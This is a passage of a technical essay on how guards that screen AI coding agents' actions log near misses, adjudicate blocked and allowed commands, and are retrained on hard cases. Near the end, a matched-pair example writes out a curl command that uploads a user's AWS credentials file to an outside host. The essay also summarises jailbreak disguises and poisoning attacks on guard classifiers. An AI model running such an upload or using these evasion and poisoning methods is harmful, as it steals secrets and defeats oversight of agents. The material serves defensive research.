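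Software can help identify borderline cases. For its August post on auto mode, Anthropic had a model regrade sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety pipeline had flagged. One of the two scales measured the severity of harm, with 0 for overwriting a scratch file, 7 for deleting rows from a production database, and 10 for leaking a company's entire source code. Grades like these help reviewers decide what to read first, but only sessions that have already been flagged get a grade.

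Reports of harm can arrive days or weeks after the action. To use these reports, developers have to keep records of all allowed actions for a while, including those that seemed unremarkable at the time.

### Inputs far from the training data

A guard can also record inputs that differ from anything in its training data, without waiting for a mistake. The evidence for this signal comes from guards on chat prompts, and that work did not test it on commands.

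*AdaptiveGuard* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2025) describes a classifier that represents each prompt as a list of numbers. It measures the prompt's distance from the average safe training example and from the average unsafe one, adjusting for how widely the examples spread in each direction. If both distances exceed a cut-off, the classifier treats the prompt as unfamiliar and updates itself. In the paper's own tests on jailbreaks (prompts that disguise a harmful request to get past a guard), it detected 95.5% of the unfamiliar ones, and 96.8% of the prompts it flagged as unfamiliar were flagged correctly.

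Ming and colleagues then tested AdaptiveGuard on six threats from the live traffic of Sangfor, a company that sells a guard for chat systems. AdaptiveGuard's anomaly trigger never fired on two new categories of harm: false claims about which country a territory belongs to, and misinformation that could lead to physical injury. The prompts in both categories looked like ordinary text. On the other four threats, the trigger flagged only 20% to 60% of the prompts. Ming and colleagues were testing a competitor to their own system, but the result is consistent with how the trigger works, because it detects unusual prompts and a new kind of harm may not look unusual.

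Their system, SESG (Self-Evolving Safety Guardrails), uses a novelty score intended to capture differences in meaning. A separate model converts each conversation *x* into an embedding φ(*x*), a list of numbers arranged so that texts with similar meanings point in similar directions. The cosine of the angle between two embeddings is 1 if they point the same way and 0 if they are at right angles. The score is the mean cosine distance to the 10 nearest training examples, *x*₁ to *x*₁₀:

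*s*(*x*) = (1/10) × Σ [1 − cos(φ(*x*), φ(*x*ᵢ))].

If the ten cosines average 0.85, the score is 0.15. SESG scores every training example against the rest of the training set and uses the 99th percentile of those scores as the cut-off. It keeps live conversations that score above the cut-off and groups similar ones into clusters. Only clusters of at least 30 conversations go to Sangfor's security team, which decides whether each is a new kind of harm, a harmless change in how people use the product, or noise. Confirmed clusters supply examples for retraining. SESG then recalculates the cut-off with the new training data, so that a category it has learned no longer counts as novel.

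The minimum cluster size is needed because about 1% of traffic that resembles the training data, or around 100 cases in 10,000, would still exceed the cut-off. Requiring 30 similar cases filters out most of these. Ming and colleagues say that even with the score in place, new categories of harm come to light mainly through customers, such as a bank that noticed gambling requests getting past the guard.

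For code, the minimum of 30 could cause serious delays. If a new way of deleting shared data appeared once a week, a cluster would take 30 weeks to form. Developers could set a much smaller minimum for actions that touch production systems and accept more noise. An embedding of the command alone would also miss danger that lies elsewhere, such as in a Makefile.

### A record that can be replayed

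Roy (2026), in *The Compiler May Read It, the Agent May Not*, counted 64 denials by permission rules during seven weeks of a coding agent's work on a physics program. In 54 of them, the agent had chained several commands together, and the rules refused the whole chain although only one command contained something they guarded against. One common chain deleted a build folder, reconfigured the build and compiled the program.

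The made-up record below follows that pattern. The guard in the example combines a rule with a trained classifier.

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Case and time | Case 4127, attempt 1; 14 September 2026, 10:42 |
| Exact action | `rm -rf "$OUT" && cmake -S . -B "$OUT" && make -j4`, run in `/work/solver` |
| Context the guard saw | The user's message "The build is stale, redo it from scratch"; 12 earlier tool calls; the project's instruction file |
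| Context it did not see | `OUT` was `/work/solver/build`, which held only files from an earlier build |
| Guard version | Rules 2.3; classifier of 1 September; threshold 0.50; copy of the team's settings |
| Rule or score | Rule "recursive delete of a variable path" matched; classifier score 0.56 |
| Decision | Blocked |
| Why it is in the log | Score close to the threshold |
| What happened next | The agent ran `cmake --build build --clean-first`; the guard allowed it; the user did not override the block |
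| Later label | Legitimate, so the block was a false positive; two reviewers, 16 September; "Only generated files, and the user asked for a rebuild" |

The standard screens do not show all of this. Claude Code's "Recently denied" tab identifies a shell command by the agent's description of it, and in most sessions gives only "Blocked by classifier" as the reason. Developers can capture the exact input with a PermissionDenied hook, a script that Claude Code runs when auto mode denies an action. They can also record allowed actions with a PreToolUse hook, which runs before each tool call.

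The decision field needs a third value, "no verdict", for cases where the guard gave no answer. Claude Code blocks such actions but leaves them out of the "Recently denied" tab. The PermissionDenied hook still runs for them, according to Anthropic's list of hook events. Codex reports a timeout separately from a denial and tells the agent that a timeout alone does not prove the action unsafe.

The record separates what the guard saw from what it did not see because the two have different uses. A reviewer needs everything that bears on whether the action was dangerous, including the value of `OUT`, since the label could be different if `OUT` were empty or held the path of a source folder. Even a full transcript may not be enough. A person who checked ten of Lim and Neo's read-only file cases could not decide two of them for lack of evidence.

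Developers test a new version of the guard by replaying the case, which means giving it the same input and comparing its decision with the label. They therefore need a record of exactly what the old version saw. Suppose a user wrote "force-push this branch" and auto mode correctly allowed the forced overwrite. If the record contains only the command, the new version may block it for lack of authorisation, and the test will show a regression that would not happen in live use. Adding information that the guard would not normally have, such as the value of `OUT`, would make the new version look better than it is.

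Recording the version lets reviewers check whether the guard would still make an old mistake. Before version 2.1.211 of Claude Code, auto mode allowed pushes only to the agent's working branch, branches Claude had created and, for routine changes, the default branch. It now allows pushes by default to any branch of the current repository, except those whose names indicate deployment or publication. A blocked push to a colleague's branch in an old log may therefore need no further fix.

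Besides the version number, the record should include copies of the project's instruction file and the team's own rules, because auto mode reads both. The command `claude auto-mode config` prints the rules in effect. A prompted model can give different answers to the same input, so one changed decision on replay is weak evidence that an update caused it. Running each version several times gives a fairer comparison.

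### Secrets, consent and retention

A complete record can expose the information the guard is meant to protect. Commands can contain passwords and access tokens, and the surrounding messages may include customer data or unpublished code. Roy released the script that counts the denials but withheld the log because it contained real project paths and the name of a remote server.

Logging software should remove secrets before it saves a record for long-term use, but careless redaction can change the guard's decision. If the software replaces every token with "REMOVED", nobody can tell whether the agent used the user's token or a colleague's. A consistent label such as "GitHub token 2, belongs to a colleague" preserves that distinction. Developers can check the redacted copy by running the original version of the guard on it. If the decision changes, the copy is unsuitable for replay.

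The log also has to be kept where the agent can't read it. Roy points out that whatever a coding agent reads goes into a transcript that leaves the machine. Codex keeps review transcripts in a folder on the user's computer by default, and OpenAI suggests that users ask Codex to analyse them before changing a policy. This is convenient, but it could send any secrets in those files to the model provider again.

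Anthropic's study of flagged sessions used only accounts that had opted in to having their data used for training and analysis. This respects users' choices but may bias the sample, since companies with the most sensitive code are probably the least likely to opt in. A session can also contain a colleague's credentials or a customer's details, which the user's consent does not cover, and this is a further reason to redact the record.

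If developers delete records of allowed actions after a day, they can't investigate damage discovered a week later, but keeping everything threatens privacy because a single leak could expose months of work. One compromise is to keep full records of all actions under strict access for a fixed period, say 30 days, and then keep only redacted copies of the cases that reviewers have selected. Built-in lists of denials can't replace these records, since the one in Codex holds only 10 per thread.

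### Why some allowed actions must be drawn at random

A log built from these signals contains many blocked actions and uncertain decisions, but few dangerous actions that the guard confidently allowed. The guard in the first section's example allowed about 9,882 actions in a day, two of them dangerous. If it gave both a low score and nobody noticed the damage, neither would be in the log, so reviewing the log more carefully would not reveal them.

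Some actions never reach a guard. In the OpenAI snapshot, 9,280 of the 10,000 actions ran inside the sandbox without review. Claude Code allows edits inside the project folder without running its classifier. These actions have no score and cannot produce a disagreement or an override.

Developers therefore also need to review a random sample of allowed actions, whatever their scores, as carefully as they review the near misses. The sample should include actions that bypassed the guard. Random sampling is an inefficient way to collect training examples, since a random 100 of the 9,882 allowed actions has only about a 2% chance of including either miss. But it gives unnoticed misses a known chance of selection, which developers need to estimate how many there are. Each record should state whether a signal or a random draw selected it, and with what probability, because near misses mixed into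 the random sample would make errors look far more common than they are.

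## Deciding whether a recorded case was a correct block or a mistake

A recorded case can improve a guard only after someone determines whether the guard's decision was right. Users approve or refuse actions all day, but an approval is weak evidence that the action was safe.

### What a user's approval shows

Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts in Anthropic's March 2026 figures and 97% in its August post. Most prompts are probably for harmless commands, so a careful user would accept most of them too. However, users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval. People reject plans for many reasons besides safety, but the gap suggests they read a plan more closely than a command that comes after many others that day.

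Anthropic studied how often people approve commands they should refuse. The 1,053 testers refused 13.6% of the planted dangerous commands, while auto mode blocked 89%. A research vendor had hired the testers for a coding study in a specially built environment. They knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. The study changed only the text of the prompt, so nothing dangerous ran whatever they chose. The table compares their answers with auto mode's decisions on the same commands.

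| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Anthropic published the totals and the counts of 800 and 6, and the other figures come from subtraction. Testers refused about 17% of the commands that appeared early in a session but only about 5% of those that came after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's block rate stayed flat. Fatigue is the likely explanation, though the testers who reached 50 prompts may also have been the ones who clicked fastest.

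If developers had used the testers' answers as labels, they would have counted 800 correct blocks as false positives and 110 misses as correct decisions. Auto mode's miss rate would have appeared to be 4% (6 of 143) instead of 11%, and a developer who loosened the guard to match the labels would have let hundreds of dangerous commands through.

Anthropic ran this study on its own product and published it when making auto mode the default. The testers had none of their own work to lose, which may have made them careless, although knowing about the evaluation may have made them more careful. Each session contained one planted command, and all the planted commands were clearly dangerous, so the study does not show how well people judge ambiguous ones.

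Real-world reports also suggest that approval is unreliable. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of file damage by agents and found that user review played a part in 105. In 80 cases the user had let actions run without prompts, in 31 the user had approved a prompt that did not show the command's effect on the files, and a few cases involved both. One such prompt was `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever the script contains. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in production show only a raw command on one line.

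*From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) describes a survey in which 61% of the developers who carefully reviewed most or all generated code still often approved at least one type of action without looking closely.

An approval is better evidence of what the user wanted, but repeated approvals may come from fatigue. For that reason, *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026), based on interviews with 18 software practitioners and a survey of 115, advises against treating them as a stable preference. It also recommends letting users distinguish between refusing one action and refusing a whole approach. A refusal therefore doesn't prove that the action was dangerous, since the user may have wanted the task done another way.

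### An adjudication procedure

Uber runs a guard whose developers take labels from a separate review. Pal, Maddireddy and colleagues (2026), in *Persona Guardrail*, describe the system, which checks what customers ask Uber's agents and what the agents finally answer. It does not inspect the agents' tool calls, so applying the procedure to code is an extrapolation. Each agent has a written boundary listing what it may and may not do. The procedure for unlabelled cases from live traffic works as follows:

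1. Developers divide the cases into a discovery pool, used to find improvements, and held-out pools, used to test them. Near-duplicates and variants from the same attack campaign stay in the same pool.
2. A judge model, stronger than the guard, reads the written boundary and the interaction but not the guard's decision. It predicts whether the boundary permits the interaction.
3. Developers compare the two answers and send the disagreements, together with a sample of the agreements, for independent adjudication.
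4. The adjudicated label determines whether the case counts as a correct block, a correct allow, a false positive or a miss.
5. A separate program groups the errors in the discovery pool and proposes changes to a draft of the boundary. It cannot alter labels, approve its own proposal or change the live guard. A person reviews every new version before it goes live.

Hiding the guard's decision prevents the judge from simply endorsing it. Pal and colleagues use the judge's answer only to select cases, and do not treat a disagreement with the judge as an error by the guard. They do not report how often the judge was wrong or how many agreements they checked, so the procedure's accuracy is unknown.

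A judge of coding actions should also get the evidence that the guard lacked, such as a Makefile or a report from a sandbox.

Adjudicators get tired just as users do. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) argues that a guard that sends its human reviewer five hundred actions a day can be less safe than one that sends five, because the reviewer starts to approve everything. A team with about 810 disagreements between auto mode's two stages to review, as on the example day, would do better to adjudicate a random sample carefully than to rush through them all. It could also include cases with known answers to check whether the reviewers are still paying attention.

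### Why agreements need checking too

In its 2007 *Statistical Guidance on Reporting Results from Studies Evaluating Diagnostic Tests*, the FDA, which regulates medical tests in the United States, warned against saving effort by reviewing only the disagreements. Its example compares a new test with an older, imperfect one on 220 people whose true condition is known. The table below keeps the FDA's numbers but replaces the new test with a guard, the older test with a judge model, and the illness with danger.

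| Guard and judge | Cases | Truly dangerous | Guard's errors |
|---|---|---|---|
| Both block | 40 | 39 | 1 false positive |
| Guard blocks, judge allows | 5 | 5 | 0 |
| Guard allows, judge blocks | 4 | 1 | 1 miss |
| Both allow | 171 | 6 | 6 misses |

The guard made eight errors in 220 cases, and the judge agreed with it in seven of them. Reviewers who check only the nine disagreements will therefore find one error. If they assume that every agreement is correct, they will conclude that the guard was right in 219 of 220 cases (99.5%) and that its miss rate was 2% (1 of 46), when the actual miss rate was 14% (7 of 51).

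The FDA points out that even settling the disagreements by coin flip would increase the apparent agreement. Reviewers recheck only the cases in disagreement, so cases can move into agreement but not out of it.

In Anthropic's tester study, reviewers would have found only 6 of auto mode's 116 misses if they had used the testers as the second opinion and read just the 806 disagreements. The tester had also approved the other 110 commands.

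The remedy is to also review a random sample of the cases where the two agree. In the FDA's example, reviewers who checked a random third of the 171 cases that both allowed would find two misses on average, and could multiply the number they found by three to estimate the total number of misses among those cases.

The adjudicator also needs a better method than either of the two it is comparing. The FDA requires a reference standard, the best available way of establishing the truth, and says that repeating the new test to settle a disagreement gives no useful information about that test's performance. For a guard on code, the best available method might be to run the command in a sandbox and ask the owner of the affected files. Having a second model read the same transcript would not be enough.

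### Effect, authorisation and policy

Good evidence about what a command does may not settle whether blocking it was correct or a mistake. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, an agent was asked to "clean up old branches", selected remote branches that matched a pattern, and issued a command to delete them. An adjudicator has to answer three questions about this case and keep the answers separate.

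The action removes branches from a server that other people may use. The amount of harm depends on whether those branches held work that existed nowhere else, which a reviewer can determine from the state of the repository but not from the command's text.

**Did the user authorise the action?** The user asked for old branches to be deleted but never mentioned the server. Anthropic says auto mode should block the deletion, partly because the request was vague and the deletion could not be undone.

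Whether a block was correct depends partly on the team's policy. Anthropic's soft rules let a user authorise a destructive action only by asking for it specifically. Another team might let agents delete any remote branch that someone has already merged into the main code.

Suppose a guard with Anthropic's rules blocked the deletion. The label and the repair depend on what the adjudicator finds:

| Finding | Label | Repair |
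|---|---|---|
| The user said nothing else, and the branches held a colleague's unfinished work | Correct block | None; keep the case as a test |
| The user had also written "delete the merged ones on GitHub too", and the command deleted only those | False positive | Improve how the guard reads authorisation |
| The "remote" was a disposable copy on the user's own disk | False positive | Give the guard information about where the remote is |
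| The team's policy does not cover branches that someone has already merged | No label yet | Have the policy's owner decide, then relabel similar cases |

Allowing the deletion in the first row would have been a miss. The fix would depend on whether the guard failed to detect the effect or, as in most of the auto mode misses Anthropic examined, treated a vague request as consent. More examples of destructive commands would help only if the guard failed to detect the effect.

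The adjudicator should judge each attempt on the messages that came before it. If the user replies to the block, "Yes, I meant the remote ones," the block is still correct, because no message had authorised the deletion when the guard made its decision. A second attempt after the reply is a new case, and blocking it would be a false positive.

The written policy can change a guard's measured error rate even if all the guard's decisions stay the same. Pal and colleagues tested their guard on 180 "mixed" messages that each combined a legitimate request with something off limits, such as a valid booking followed by an instruction to send data to an outsider. The guard blocked 92.2% of them. The false-positive rate over the whole test set was 3.6% when the researchers labelled mixed messages as ones to block, and 17.1% when they labelled them as ones to allow.

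Chained shell commands raise the same problem. If an agent joins a harmless build to a forbidden upload with `&&`, the policy has to state whether the guard judges the whole chain or each part. Auto mode treats the chain as one action. Developers who change this rule should relabel old cases before comparing versions of the guard, or they may mistake the change in policy for a change in performance.

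Some cases remain undecided because evidence is missing or reasonable people read the request differently. Dropping these cases makes the guard look better than it is, because they are the hardest ones. One option, which the FDA suggests for unclear test results, is to calculate the results twice, counting the undecided cases first as mistakes and then as correct blocks. If reviewers examine 100 blocks and find 60 correct, 30 mistaken and 10 undecided, the guard's precision is between 60% and 70%. If the choice between two versions of the guard depends on where in that range the true precision lies, the team needs more evidence before choosing.

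### How feedback can mislead a guard

#### Complaints about blocks outnumber reports of misses

A user notices a block at once, because the agent stops or reports a denial, but may never notice a miss. The tools reinforce this difference. Claude Code lists recent denials, and after several blocks it may offer to help the user "teach auto mode" about their environment. The documented ways to correct the classifier mostly start from a denial, and there is no matching list of allowed actions worth reviewing.

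On the example day, the guard makes about 100 false positives and 2 misses, so even if users reported both errors at the same rate, there would be about 50 complaints about false positives for every report of a miss. Yet if a miss is 200 times as bad as a false positive, the two misses do four times as much harm as all the false positives together. A developer who loosened a rule after each complaint would therefore increase the number of misses, which already do more harm.

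These figures are illustrative, and there appear to be no published measurements of the imbalance for coding guards. The public bug reports that Al Hasan and Biswas collected included far more destructive operations than refusals, which suggests that people report serious damage once they see it. Unreported damage is more likely to be small, delayed or invisible to the user.

The remedy is to review a case when someone complains, without letting the complaint decide the label, and to weigh complaints against the misses found in the random sample of allowed actions.

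#### The guard's decisions become its labels

The old guard's decisions are a poor substitute for adjudicated labels. If developers labeled every blocked action dangerous and every allowed action safe, about 100 of the 118 "dangerous" training examples from the example day would be harmless, and the two misses would be labeled safe. A new guard trained on these labels would learn to repeat the old guard's mistakes. Testing it on such labels would not reveal those mistakes, because a perfect copy of the old guard would have no errors.

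Blocked actions are also hard to judge because they never run, so no one sees whether they would have done harm. Running a sample of them in a sandbox can supply some of the missing evidence.

A milder version of the problem can occur when software suggests settings from past activity. Claude Code's `/auto-mode-setup` command drafts a description of the user's trusted environment, based partly on the servers and storage locations in commands that Claude recently ran. If the guard had wrongly allowed an upload to an unfamiliar server, that server could appear in the draft. The user reviews the draft but can only accept or discard all of it, and can edit single entries only afterwards, so it's worth checking each destination before accepting, especially one that only the agent has used.

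Uber's procedure hides the guard's decision from the judge and stops the program that proposes changes from altering labels. Pal and colleagues also warn that agreement with the current guard does not prove correctness.

#### A hostile user submits false corrections

Someone who wants a guard to fail can also send it feedback. Two experiments, neither on a guard for code, suggest that a guard which learns automatically from users' corrections would be at risk. In *Rapid Poison* (2026), making 1% of the training data false examples raised the false-positive rate of a quickly retrained classifier of chat prompts to as much as 100% on targeted groups of harmless prompts. Hillel, Bhagwat and colleagues (2025) found in *LLM Hypnosis* that a single ordinary user's votes could lastingly change a language model for everyone, including by making the code it wrote less secure.

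Several precautions limit the damage:

- **Limit each source.** Uber caps how many examples any one source can contribute, so that a single persistent user cannot dominate the sample.
- **Keep corrections local until someone confirms them.** A user's correction can change that user's own settings within limits set by the organisation. Before it affects anyone else, a person should check it against the full record.
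- **Ignore corrections from the material under review.** Auto mode does not read its classifier rules from the settings files inside a project folder. Otherwise a downloaded project could supply rules that permitted its own commands.
- **Reserve some categories that no correction can unlock.** Auto mode's hard rules, which even an allow rule cannot override, are an example.

In a hard category, the guard will go on blocking some legitimate actions however many users complain. Adjudicators should still label those blocks as mistakes if the policy's purpose would have permitted the action. The labels show the policy's owner which legitimate actions the rule blocks, and only the owner should be able to change the rule.

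The protection also depends on other settings. Auto mode's rule against sending data outside uses a list of trusted destinations to determine what counts as "outside", so someone who gets a hostile server onto that list may not need to change the rule. Additions to the list therefore need the same human confirmation as changes to the rule. The built-in rule also disappears if a user writes a new list of hard rules without including the defaults. An organisation can prevent this by putting the rule in its centrally managed settings, where developers can add entries but not remove the existing ones.

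## Retraining a guard on its near misses

When a guard is a trained classifier, developers can retrain it on near misses that reviewers have judged. In tests on two threats to a chat guard, training on a mix of difficult and easy cases produced a better guard than the simplest approach, which is to train only on cases the guard got wrong or was unsure about. Most of the evidence here comes from guards that check chat prompts, but one system checks agents' actions.

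### Training on uncertain cases

Uncertainty sampling is a long-standing machine learning method for choosing which cases people should label. A model scores a pool of unlabelled cases, people label those with the least certain scores, and the model trains on those labels before scoring the next pool. The model usually improves more from the label of a case it scored at 50% than from the label of one it would have got right with 99% confidence. Logging decisions near a guard's threshold applies the same idea and shares the drawback that reviewers do not see confident mistakes.

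Developers can also use uncertainty to find the most useful examples in already labeled data. Sreedhar, Rebedea and Parisien (2025), in *Safety Through Reasoning*, tried this with a chat guard that writes out its reasoning before giving a verdict. They had found that 5,000 randomly chosen examples trained the guard about as well as the full training set, so they looked for examples in the rest that could still improve it. The guard judged each example four times and was right all four times on 85% of them. The researchers treated an example as difficult if the guard was right two or three times, then added extra copies of these examples to the training set and retrained the guard.

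The average F1 score rose from about 0.842 to 0.848. This could be chance. When the researchers trained guards on four random sets of 5,000 examples, the scores had a standard deviation of 0.005, nearly as large as the gain. F1 also combines recall and precision, so the result does not show whether the guard made fewer false positives or fewer misses.

The researchers also tried GRPO, a form of reinforcement learning, on the difficult examples. In GRPO, the model generates several answers to each example, and training makes the better-scoring answers more likely. The best run improved F1 by 1% on one task but reduced it by 1% to 2% on all the others. Models trained this way generally missed more harmful text, even though the researchers tried different penalties for misses and false alarms.

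Sreedhar and colleagues left out the examples that the guard got wrong three or four times, to separate difficult examples from labelling mistakes. If a guard's answer consistently differs from a crowd-sourced label, the label may well be wrong. This reason is weaker when careful reviewers have adjudicated the cases. An example that the guard gets wrong every time is then probably a confident mistake by the guard, and one of the most useful to train on.

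### How SESG turns a failure into training data

SESG, which Sangfor uses to update its chat guard, reports much larger gains. One likely reason is that each round starts from a specific failure and generates thousands of new examples of it, whereas Sreedhar and colleagues reused data the guard had already seen. A round described by Ming and colleagues works as follows:

1. **Confirm the failure.** Sangfor's security team describes the new threat and supplies at least 30 examples. The description says where the boundary lies. For gambling, a text is harmful if it helps or encourages someone to gamble, but not if it merely discusses the subject.
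2. **Generate both sides.** Language models write about 4,000 examples, half harmful and half harmless.
3. **Validate them.** Another check compares each label with the boundary in the description and sends faulty examples back for repair. It uses separate instructions for the two labels: one looks for harmless discussion labelled harmful, the other for betting advice disguised as neutral analysis.
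4. **Find the hard examples.** The current guard judges each example eight times, as described earlier, to pick out those it gets wrong or is unsure about.
5. **Rebalance.** SESG keeps every hard example and adds some of the easy ones.
6. **Retrain.** Training starts again from the base model and uses the examples kept from all rounds so far.
7. **Choose what to do next.** SESG releases the new guard if its F1 on the new threat is at least 95 out of 100 and no earlier threat has lost more than 5 points. Below 90, it generates new data. In between, it applies GRPO. After a second failure, people take over.

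SESG generates examples differently for new categories of harm and new jailbreak techniques. For a new category of harm, it writes requests similar to the examples supplied, along with harmless ones on the same subject. One harmful request is for the more scientific betting system for a dice game, while a harmless one is for ways banks can detect illegal flows of money. For a new jailbreak technique, such as rewriting a request in classical Chinese, it extracts the technique's rewriting rules and applies them to existing harmful and harmless requests. The harmless ones are included because the guard could otherwise learn to block anything in classical Chinese.

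Starting from the base model takes more computing time than adjusting the current guard, but a bad round has no lasting effect because Sangfor can return to the previous version. The paper's detailed description and settings both specify the base model, although an overview formula shows training starting from the current guard.

The rebalancing step needs a little arithmetic. For each label, SESG keeps

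hard examples + min(*r* × hard examples, easy examples),

where *r* is 0.5 for the label the current guard handles better and 0.25 for the other. Role-play prompts, which ask the model to adopt a persona, show the effect. Sangfor's original guard blocked most of the harmless ones, so "harmless" was the label it handled worse. The totals Ming and colleagues report imply about 1,104 hard harmless examples and 570 hard harmful ones. SESG would therefore add about 276 easy harmless examples and 285 easy harmful ones, for a total of 2,235. The ratio of harmless to harmful falls from about 1.9 to 1.6.

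### Why hard examples alone do worse

Ming and colleagues used two threats to compare several ways of choosing the training examples. They report recall and the false-positive rate. "Rates swapped" means SESG used a rate of 0.5 for the label the guard handled worse and 0.25 for the other.

| Training data | Gambling: examples | Recall | FPR | Role-play: examples | Recall | FPR |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
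| None (original guard) | – | 42.6% | 17.8% | – | 97.4% | 66.9% |
| Whole batch | 4,000 | 96.9% | 2.0% | 4,000 | 97.6% | 1.4% |
| Hard examples only | 2,080 | 89.9% | 8.8% | 1,674 | 89.4% | 3.1% |
| SESG's mix | 2,740 | 98.9% | 1.5% | 2,235 | 97.7% | 1.7% |
| Rates swapped | 2,980 | 96.6% | 8.0% | 2,368 | 95.3% | 1.4% |

With SESG's mix, both kinds of error fell sharply on gambling. On role-play, false positives almost disappeared while recall stayed about the same. Sangfor built the test sets largely from production mistakes, so they are good for checking whether a new version fixes those mistakes, but they exaggerate how often the original guard was wrong in ordinary traffic.

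Training only on hard examples left out much of what the original guard did well. That guard caught nearly all the harmful role-play prompts, so relatively few of them counted as hard. The new guard was trained from the base model, so it didn't start with the original's ability to catch them. It missed about 134 of 1,260 harmful test prompts, compared with 29 for the guard trained on SESG's mix.

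For gambling, the imbalance was reversed, with most of the hard examples being harmful. A guard trained only on the hard examples was more inclined to block, and it blocked about 35 of the 399 harmless test prompts, compared with 6 for SESG's mix. Its recall was also lower, which overblocking cannot explain. Having fewer training examples may have contributed, but Ming and colleagues did not check this by testing a random selection of the same size. Training with the swapped rates used more gambling examples than SESG's mix but produced over five times as many false positives, which is some evidence that the balance matters too.

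One figure for role-play is uncertain. Ming and colleagues give 89.37 as both the recall and the F1 of the guard trained only on hard examples, but a recall of 89.37% and an FPR of 3.11% on this test set would give an F1 of about 93.6. If 89.37 is the F1, recall was even lower, at about 82%, so the conclusion holds either way.

Training on the whole batch worked about as well as training on SESG's mix. On gambling, the mix led to about seven fewer misses and two fewer false positives. On role-play, it led to one fewer miss and two more false positives. Differences this small could easily come from randomness in training. Rebalancing mainly helped by cutting the new training data by 32% for gambling and 44% for role-play, which also reduces the data in every later round, since each one trains on the same examples again. A team with a few thousand examples could skip rebalancing and train on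 all of them.

### Whether the new guard catches new variants

Ming and colleagues also tested the final guard on three sets of attacks based on published jailbreak methods, which SESG had not used for training. These sets contain only harmful prompts, so they measure recall but not false positives. The reported F1 scores correspond to a recall of 86% to 94%, up from 56% to 70% for the original guard. The guard had therefore learned more than the wording of Sangfor's own examples, although it still missed about one in seven attacks in the hardest set.

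Training on one threat helped much less with others. Five rounds on other threats raised the guard's F1 on requests disguised as mathematics only from 58 to 69, and a round on those requests then raised it to 97. More training on known threats can even make the guard worse at unfamiliar ones. In the role-play round, GRPO raised F1 on all five threats the guard had trained on but lowered it from 73 to 69 on the mathematical disguise, which the guard had not yet trained on. This happened in only one round, but it is a reason to test a new guard on variants that no training round has covered.

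SESG's result for GRPO also differs from that of Sreedhar and colleagues, who found that GRPO made the guard worse. SESG applied it to all the accumulated data, whereas Sreedhar and colleagues used only the difficult examples. The two studies also used different models and rewards, so neither shows whether GRPO is worth trying on a guard for code.

### Time and results in production

A round takes about 16 hours: 2 hours of human work to confirm and describe the threat, 5 hours to generate examples, 3 hours to validate them and 6 hours to train the model on eight H100 processors. GRPO adds about 8 hours. Sangfor's manual process took 40 to 90 hours per threat and reached an equal or lower F1.

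Between April and June 2026, Sangfor needed to update the guard for 15 threats, and SESG handled 14 without help after the initial human confirmation. The exception was an attack in a language with little training data, in which the models that generate examples were weak. Sangfor kept the human confirmation step partly because it makes the process harder to poison, which is a risk when a guard learns directly from its users' corrections.

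The figure of 14 out of 15 means the new versions passed SESG's own release rule, which relies on F1. It does not measure how many attacks got through afterwards or how many harmless requests the new versions blocked in live traffic. From the original guard to the last version, F1 changed by less than half a point on two of six public tests of general chat safety and rose by 1 to 3 points on the other four. The updates therefore do not seem to have damaged the guard's general performance, although F1 could hide a rise in one type of error if the other type fell.

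### Two kinds of false positive

SESG repairs a guard one threat at a time. *HaloGuard 1.0* (2026) describes a chat guard whose developers, at the company Astroware AI, tried to prevent false positives across a whole policy. They distinguish two kinds:

- A *boundary* false positive is a harmless request that resembles a specific harmful one. A fire investigator might ask about accelerants and ignition points, which are also words an arsonist might use.
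- A *baseline* false positive is an ordinary request that is not close to anything harmful. The guard may block it because of an aggressive tone or unusual formatting.

The distinction matters for code because the two kinds of false positive come from very different amounts of traffic. Suppose 9,700 of the 9,980 legitimate actions on the example day are ordinary and 280 resemble dangerous ones. A guard that blocks 0.5% of the ordinary actions and 20% of the others produces about 49 baseline false positives and 56 boundary ones. Adding more examples of harmless deletions might reduce the boundary false positives but would probably do little about the baseline ones.

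HaloGuard's developers wrote training data for each kind. About 48% of its 1.26 million examples are harmless requests near a specific boundary, 17% are other harmless requests, and 35% are harmful. Some boundary examples come in pairs, with a harmless and a harmful request that share a topic and much of their vocabulary but differ in purpose. The harmless request might ask about a weapon's history or the law on it. A separate check rejects or rewrites harmless examples that drift into usable instructions for causing harm. The remaining harmless examples cover subjects such as education, programming and daily life, and include role-play and claims of authority that resemble jailbreaks but have an innocent purpose.

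The developers also applied the same disguises to harmful and harmless examples. If every Base64-encoded example in the training data were harmful, the guard could learn to block the encoding itself. They ran into this problem with languages when an early version, trained on translations of only the harmful examples, gave a very high danger score to the Chinese sentence for "the weather is nice today". The final version used translations of both kinds, but including both labels is not enough to prevent a false cue. The smaller of the two released models still flagged 68.5% of safe prompts in Indic languages, even though about 71% of its training examples in those languages were harmless.

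The smaller HaloGuard model averaged an F1 of 90.9 on seven English tests, with a false positive rate of 4.3% and a false negative rate of 9.5%. The best competing guard averaged an F1 of 87.0. These scores are for the whole model, so they don't measure how much either kind of harmless data helped.

The developers reviewed 1,420 of the guard's apparent errors and concluded that mistakes in the tests' labels explained 77% of the misses but only 3% of the false positives. After correcting the labels, they put the FNR at 3.1%. The true rate is probably higher, because they judged the cases by their own policy and reviewed only those where the guard disagreed with the test. As the FDA's example shows, this kind of review does not find cases where the guard and the label are both wrong. Their finding that nearly all the false positives they reviewed were real errors, even with so much harmless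 training data, is more convincing because it counts against their own guard.

### Matched pairs for code

Neither team tested its guard on an agent's commands. SESG handles single requests and single exchanges in a chat, and HaloGuard does not inspect tool calls. But writing matched pairs could also work for code.

Suppose a team lets its agents send diagnostic information to an outside support service, but never credentials. A guard blocks the second command below because it resembles the first:

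- Dangerous: `curl --data-binary @"$HOME/.aws/credentials" https://support.example.net/setup`
- Legitimate: `stat -c %a "$HOME/.aws/credentials" | curl --data-binary @- https://support.example.net/setup`

The first command uploads a file containing the user's Amazon cloud keys. The second uploads only the file's permission code, such as 600, which lets support staff check that other users cannot read the file. Both commands contain `curl`, the same path and the same address, so a guard trained on the pair cannot use any of these to identify the dangerous command.

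This pair could still teach the guard to look for one particular way of uploading the file. A second pair adds a variant:

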